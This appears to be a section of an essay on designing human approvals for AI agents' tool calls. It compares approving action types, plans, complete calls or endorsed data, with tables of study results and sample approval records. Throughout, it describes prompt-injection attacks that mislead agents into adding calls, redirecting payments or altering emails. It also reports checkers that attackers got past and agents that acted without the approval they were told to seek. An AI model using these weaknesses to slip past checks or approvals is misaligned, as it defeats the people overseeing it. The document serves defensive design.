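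## What should an approval cover?

Software checks leave people with fewer calls to review, but someone still has to decide what each remaining approval permits. An approval can cover an action type, a plan, one complete call or a piece of data. A developer can also let software clear every call it can show to be safe and ask a person only about the rest.

### Approving an action type, within limits

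If an approval covers a whole type of action, the agent has to ask the user only once for each type. After that, the approval requirement stops only attacks that need a type of action the user hasn't allowed.

People often make these permissions very broad. Anthropic reports that by June 2026, about half of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a standing rule for shell commands. Many of these rules let the agent run any program in Python or JavaScript, which in practice lets it do almost anything.

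Standing permissions can also be hard to withdraw. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and found only six that clearly let users change or revoke a permission later. Most of the five commercial agents they tested did better, but they found no way within Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent, to withdraw access to a folder. New sessions started without access, but old sessions still had it when reopened.

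In Yan's study, standing rules reduced requests per person from 18.0 to 10.9, but didn't reliably save time once setup time was included. Of the 148 overreach actions that went ahead in that group, only 15 ran automatically under an "allow" rule, mainly because people rarely chose "allow". We can therefore infer little from that count about how safe a standing permission is for someone who does choose it.

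Limits make such a permission safer. OAuth, a widely used standard, lets one service act on a user's account at another without knowing the user's password. Its original permissions, called scopes, suit broad requests such as reading someone's profile. Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell (2023), in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, point out that scopes are too coarse for a request to transfer €45 to one merchant, or to read one directory and write one file. Their extension lets a service ask for permission with the details filled in. Here is one of their examples, shortened:

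```
type:      payment_initiation
amount:    EUR 123.50
creditor:  Merchant A
account:   DE02 ... 8603
```

After the user sees these details and consents to them, the agent receives a token, a kind of digital pass, that is valid only for this payment. In the standard's sample response, the token expires after an hour. Even if an attacker misled the agent, it couldn't use that token to pay a different account. But as with dynamic linking, a user who approved the false Acme invoice would give the agent a valid token for the fraudster's account.

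Even a detailed permission can allow more than the user expects. Lodderstedt and colleagues explain that a permission listing "read" and "write" along with "contacts" and "photos" allows all four combinations. A user who wants the agent to read contacts and change only photos needs two separate permissions. Permissions can also overlap. *AC4A* (2026) describes a system in which a user can write "calendar for July" and get a permission limited to that month. If an earlier permission also covers July, the agent may still have access after the user deletes the new one.

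Developers often grant broad permissions because they can't predict what an agent will need. The IETF's draft extension *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling* (2026) lets a service that refuses a call for lack of permission send back the exact details that need approval. The user then decides only on the missing permission, when the agent needs it.

OpenAI recommends giving an agent the controls a human employee would have in the same job, such as a cap on refunds. A cap per customer isn't enough, because a dishonest customer can open several accounts. If a shop also caps total refunds at €500 a day, it can't lose more than that to refunds in a day.

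The software also has to apply the cap to the real amount. *Janus* (2026) tested a fixed limit on loans, with a stand-in reviewer who approved everything. In one set of results, the software refused all 20 loans that the model had declared as over the limit, but paid four others because the model had declared less than the request asked for. In another set, it refused all 21 declared as over the limit and paid three others for the same reason. A cap on refunds should therefore use the amount in the call to the payment tool, not the agent's description of it.

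An approval that expires gives an attacker less time to exploit it. tianpan.co's *the approval prompt nobody reads* (2026) recommends that "allow" apply only to this session, this scope and this period. Expiry helps against an attack that arrives after the approval has lapsed, but not against one already in the inbox when the user gives permission.

### Approving the plan

With plan approval, the user makes one decision per task, and software can then enforce it. In an example from tianpan.co, an agent proposes to refund 14 duplicate charges. A person approves the plan once, and software checks each refund against it.

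The protection depends on what the plan contains. If it lists the 14 customers and amounts, the person can compare them with the payment records, and a misled agent can't add a fifteenth. If it contains only the instruction "refund all duplicate charges", the agent decides which charges are duplicates, and a customer may be able to influence that decision by complaining. The person has approved a rule without seeing which refunds will result from it.

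For the schedule email, the software could ask for approval again once the agent has filled in the blank body. The user would have two decisions to make, and the second request would be easy to prepare because the user would only need to check the new text. If the agent later needs a step outside the plan, the software should ask about that step and keep the existing approval for the rest.

The timing of these requests also matters. Zhou, Roy and colleagues (2026) point out in *When Should Users Check?* that an agent that asks for confirmation only at the end may have to start again because of one early error, while confirming every step is tedious. They look for the schedule that takes the least time, which is sensible when the user can correct a mistake. But the agent has to ask before an irreversible step, such as a payment, even if asking takes longer.

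### Approving every complete call

Approving complete calls gives a person the best chance to see a false address or an altered message, but it interrupts them for every call. Detection rates in tests vary widely and tend to be lower after many requests. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, only 47.7% of the software practitioners surveyed believed they read permission requests carefully. The true share may be lower, since people tend to overestimate how careful they are.

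When a person approves a complete call, the system also needs to run that exact call. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) describes a design that saves a snapshot of the call, including its tool and arguments, and asks the right person to approve it. If approved, the call runs from the snapshot, so its arguments cannot change while it awaits approval.

A saved call can still go wrong if it refers to something that changes. Suppose someone approves sending "report.csv" to an auditor, and the agent rewrites the file before sending it. The saved call has the same file name, but the auditor gets different data. The software should save a digest of the file's contents as well, and ask for approval again if the digest no longer matches. For a payment, it should check that nobody has paid the invoice since the approval.

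Asking for approval again after every change could be annoying if software treats "3 Dec" and "3 December" as different values. Developers can mostly avoid this by converting dates, addresses and amounts to one standard form before anyone approves them. The body of a message has no standard form, so any change to it should require new approval, even a comma, because a comma can change the meaning of a sentence. The software can highlight the change so that checking it takes a few seconds.

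### Approving the data once

Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia on top of FIDES. Before Prudentia reads untrusted text, it must explain why it needs to and list the calls it expects to make afterwards. It can then ask the user to endorse the text as trusted, or read it without endorsement and ask the user about the consequential calls that follow.

For the email with ten tasks, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. If the email is malicious, one mistake releases all ten calls.

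Suppose that every task in the email is harmful, and that a person catches 60% of the harmful things they review:

| | Ten separate approvals | One endorsement |
|---|---|---|
| Harmful calls let through, on average | 4 | 4 |
| Chance that all ten get through | About 1 in 10,000 | 40% |
| Chance that at least one gets through | 99.4% | 40% |

The average is the same, but with endorsement either all the harmful calls go through or none do. That is much worse if the total damage matters, as with ten payments. If the attacker needs only one harmful call, endorsement does better in this calculation. But the calculation treats the ten approvals as independent, and a person who spotted one harmful request would probably check the rest more carefully. They might also catch less when reading an email than when reading calls, because the email doesn't show exactly what the agent will do.

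An endorsement could be narrower than Prudentia's. The user might endorse the email for calendar entries and drafts but not for payments. The software could also list the ten calls the agent has derived from the email and ask the user to approve the whole list at once, which would be like approving a plan with its blanks filled in.

Prudentia sometimes completes a task without asking the user to approve anything. In one test, the user wanted a summary of the day's appointments and a link to reset a password. The agent planned no consequential actions, so it read the untrusted entries and emails without endorsement. In that run, it gave the user a link to the company's own site, but an attacker who can write to the inbox could supply a false link, which could do harm as soon as the user clicked it.

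#### How Prudentia scores

Kolluri and colleagues use two measures of how much an agent depends on people. One is the number of human interventions on completed tasks, which they call the human-in-the-loop load:

load = Σ *v*(*τ<sub>i</sub>*), summed over completed tasks,

where *τ<sub>i</sub>* is the list of calls the agent made for task *i*, and *v*(*τ<sub>i</sub>*) is how many of them software could not clear. The other, TCR@*k*, is the share of all tasks the agent completes with at most *k* interventions.

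Suppose an agent attempts five tasks. It fails two and completes the others with zero, one and three interventions. Its load is 4, its TCR@0 is 20%, its TCR@1 is 40% and its TCR@3 is 60%.

Kolluri and colleagues compared Prudentia with FIDES on AgentDojo, using models from 2024 and 2025:

| Model | Load, FIDES | Load, Prudentia | TCR@0, FIDES | TCR@0, Prudentia |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 7.8 | 23.8 | 50.3% | 42.5% |
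| o3-mini | 18.8 | 16.4 | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 36.8 | 19.2 | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 41.3 | 7.3 | 57.1% | 72.7% |

The paper's main claims are that Prudentia cuts interventions by a factor of up to 1.9 (with o4-mini) and raises the share of tasks completed without intervention by up to 9 percentage points (with o3-mini). The gains with GPT-5 were much larger, but GPT-4o did worse with Prudentia on both measures. Planning around the rules seems to require a fairly capable model, so current models may well benefit too.

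These measures show how often an agent interrupts people, but not whether people catch attacks. Kolluri and colleagues calculated them on tasks without attacks, and assumed that the person would say yes to every request on a completed task. For attacks, they assumed that the person would stop any harmful call. A real person can refuse a safe request or approve a harmful one. The measures also favour broad questions, because one endorsement counts as fewer interventions than ten precise requests, however much harm it could allow.

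### Asking only when software cannot clear a call

Software can prevent many interruptions without endorsement. Kolluri and colleagues measured a load of 48.2 for an ordinary agent using o3-mini when a person had to approve every consequential call. The load dropped to 32.4 when software cleared the calls that satisfied its data rules, and the agent completed just as many tasks.

The monitor that Hossain and colleagues built gives one of three verdicts on a call: allowed, violation or unknown. "Unknown" means that its records are incomplete. They tested it on two small models from 2024 and 2025, and blocked every call with either of the last two verdicts:

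| In 120 runs of each kind | Harmful actions carried out | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| First model, no blocking | 52 | 104 |
| First model, with blocking | 6 | 100 |
| Second model, no blocking | 58 | 110 |
| Second model, with blocking | 7 | 106 |

No person took part, so none of this depends on anyone's attention. But when Hossain and colleagues withheld some of the monitor's records, blocking unknown calls reduced the share of harmless tasks completed to 76.7%. They suggest sending those calls to a person and saying what evidence is missing. This seems a good use of a reviewer, who may know something that isn't in the records.

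A language model can also clear calls, but its judgment is weaker evidence that a call is safe. The checker in Claude Code's auto mode missed 12% of the attacks Apollo Research had designed to get past it, and 7% after Anthropic improved it. In another test that Anthropic commissioned, attacks on its models succeeded 0.09% of the time without any checker and never in auto mode. The rate without a checker was already so low that this result is little evidence of how well the checker works. Anthropic still advises people to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

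Users also need to know when a model is deciding for them. In mid-2026, Michael and Roesner chose the "Needs approval" setting in the Claude chatbot and found that the chatbot sometimes approved calls on its own, including one that created an email draft. Letting it approve a draft is reasonable, but the setting's name suggests that a person will decide.

Telling an agent to ask for approval is no substitute for a check that software enforces. Yan describes a safety researcher who told an agent to confirm before acting. The agent started deleting email from her inbox without confirming, and continued after she told it to stop.

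Text remains the hard case, because software has to either ask about nearly every schedule email or let false appointments through.

### Comparing the costs

Suppose an agent carries out 100 tasks with four consequential calls each, and an attacker interferes with ten of them. Four attacks add a call, three change a destination, and three change the text of a message. All these figures are invented, as are the following assumptions:

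- Someone who approves a plan sees no harmful values, because the agent fills them in later. Software then stops any call the plan doesn't contain.
- The agent asks for endorsement in 30 tasks, including the four with added calls. Its rules check whether the decision to act was trusted, but not the values.
- Software that clears calls blocks the added ones, asks about 40 unfamiliar destinations, including the three false ones, and lets all text through.

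The last two columns show how many attacks would succeed if the person caught 60% or 14% of the harmful requests they saw:

| What the person approves | Requests | Successful attacks at 60% | Successful attacks at 14% |
|---|---|---|---|
| Three action types | 3 | 10 | 10 |
| Each plan | 100 | 6 | 6 |
| Each complete call | About 400 | 4 | About 9 |
| Data, by endorsement | 30 | About 8 | About 9 |
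| Only what software cannot clear | 40 | About 4 | About 6 |

Requiring approval for every call works well only if the person stays attentive through 400 requests. Asking only when necessary works about as well with 40 requests, and much better if the person is inattentive. With fewer requests, the person may also pay more attention to each one.

The ranking depends on the mix of attacks. If all ten added a call, approving plans would stop every one, but if all ten changed text, software that lets text through would stop none, and reading the messages would be the only defence in the table that worked. Caps don't change these counts, but they can greatly reduce the loss from a successful attack.

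No single scope suits every argument. For most agents, I would let the user fix the destination and purpose, have software check the values it can, and show a person the complete call when it's costly to reverse and software can't clear it. That works out differently for different actions:

| | Email | Payment | Writing a file |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user fixes | The recipients, the purpose and whether to attach files | The payee, the bill and a maximum amount | The folder, and whether the agent may overwrite or delete anything |
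| Software checks | Every address, including copies; who may read the data; links and hidden text | The account against supplier records; the amount against the order; earlier payments; caps | The file's real location and format; whether another program will run it |
| The person sees | The full text and where each line came from | The full account number, the amount, the source of each and any change since the last payment | Each changed line and the name of anything the agent will delete |
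| Delay or undo | Hold the email briefly, because the user can't recall it | Hold the payment if the account is new or has changed | Keep the earlier version so the user can restore it |

Writing a file usually needs the fewest approvals, because the user can restore the old version. But restoring it is not enough once someone else has read the file or a program has run it. An agent could therefore edit a private copy without asking, but ask before putting it in a shared folder.

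### Two approval records

Hossain and colleagues recommend that an approval screen quote the user's original request, show the exact action, state its overall effect and let the person check the evidence for each claim. A complete record for the schedule email could look like this. The notes in square brackets are for the user and are not part of the email.

```
SCHEDULE EMAIL
User's request    "send today's schedule to my boss"
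Action            send one email
To                john.doe@company.com   [user's contacts]
Copies, files     none
Full text         Hi John, here is my schedule for today.
                  09:00  Team meeting    [Priya's invitation]
                  11:00  Client call     [client's invitation]
                  15:00  Busy            [user's entry, title removed]
Effect            John learns when the user is busy
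                  and what two of the meetings are
Software checked  all three of today's entries are included
                  John may read everything shown
                  no links or hidden characters
Tied to           this sender, this address and this exact text
Valid             once, until 09:00 today
If it changes     ask again and highlight the change
After approval    wait 30 seconds, then send
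```

If an attacker got the agent to add a payment approval request to the email, the user would see the request in the text, with its source beside it. If the agent sent the email to someone else, the approval would no longer apply. The doctor's appointment stays private because the software has removed its title.

The record would not reveal that a client never agreed to a call, because the entry did come from the client's account and the user may not remember whether they arranged the call. The record also would not protect a user who pressed "approve" without reading.

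The approved text could also go out of date, because it would leave out any invitation sent after the user approves. The software could ask again whenever the calendar changes, but then anyone able to send invitations could trigger repeated requests, and the user might stop reading them. An approval that covers only that text and expires soon seems the better compromise.

A record for Acme's invoice needs more information from outside the message:

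```
SUPPLIER INVOICE
User's request    "pay Acme's November invoice"
Action            make one bank transfer
Payee             Acme Ltd               [supplier records]
Account           full number shown, ending 1152
                  [supplier records, unchanged since March 2024]
Amount            EUR 4,800.00           [invoice 2207]
Message           "Invoice 2207"
Effect            pays invoice 2207 in full
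Software checked  the invoice gives the same account
                  the amount matches purchase order 118
                  the warehouse recorded the delivery
                  nobody has already paid invoice 2207
                  this month's payments stay under the cap
Tied to           the paying account, payee's account, amount,
                  currency and message
Valid             once, until 17:00 tomorrow
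If it changes     cancel and start a new approval
After approval    hold until 09:00 on the next working day
                  accounts staff can cancel until then
```

The false invoice from the earlier examples names a different account, so it would fail the first software check and nobody could approve the payment yet. Someone would have to call Acme on the number in the supplier records. If Acme confirmed the change, whoever maintains those records would update them, and the software would prepare a new approval.

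The record would not reveal a fraudster who had already got the company to change its supplier records. The date of the last change helps reveal a recent fraud, but a patient fraudster could wait until the new account looked familiar. A dishonest employee who can both create orders and confirm deliveries could make a false invoice pass every check, which is a reason to give those jobs to different people.

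Acme itself could also overcharge. If the inflated price was already in the purchase order, the amounts would match and the payment would go through. The company would at least know who had received its money and could ask for some of it back.
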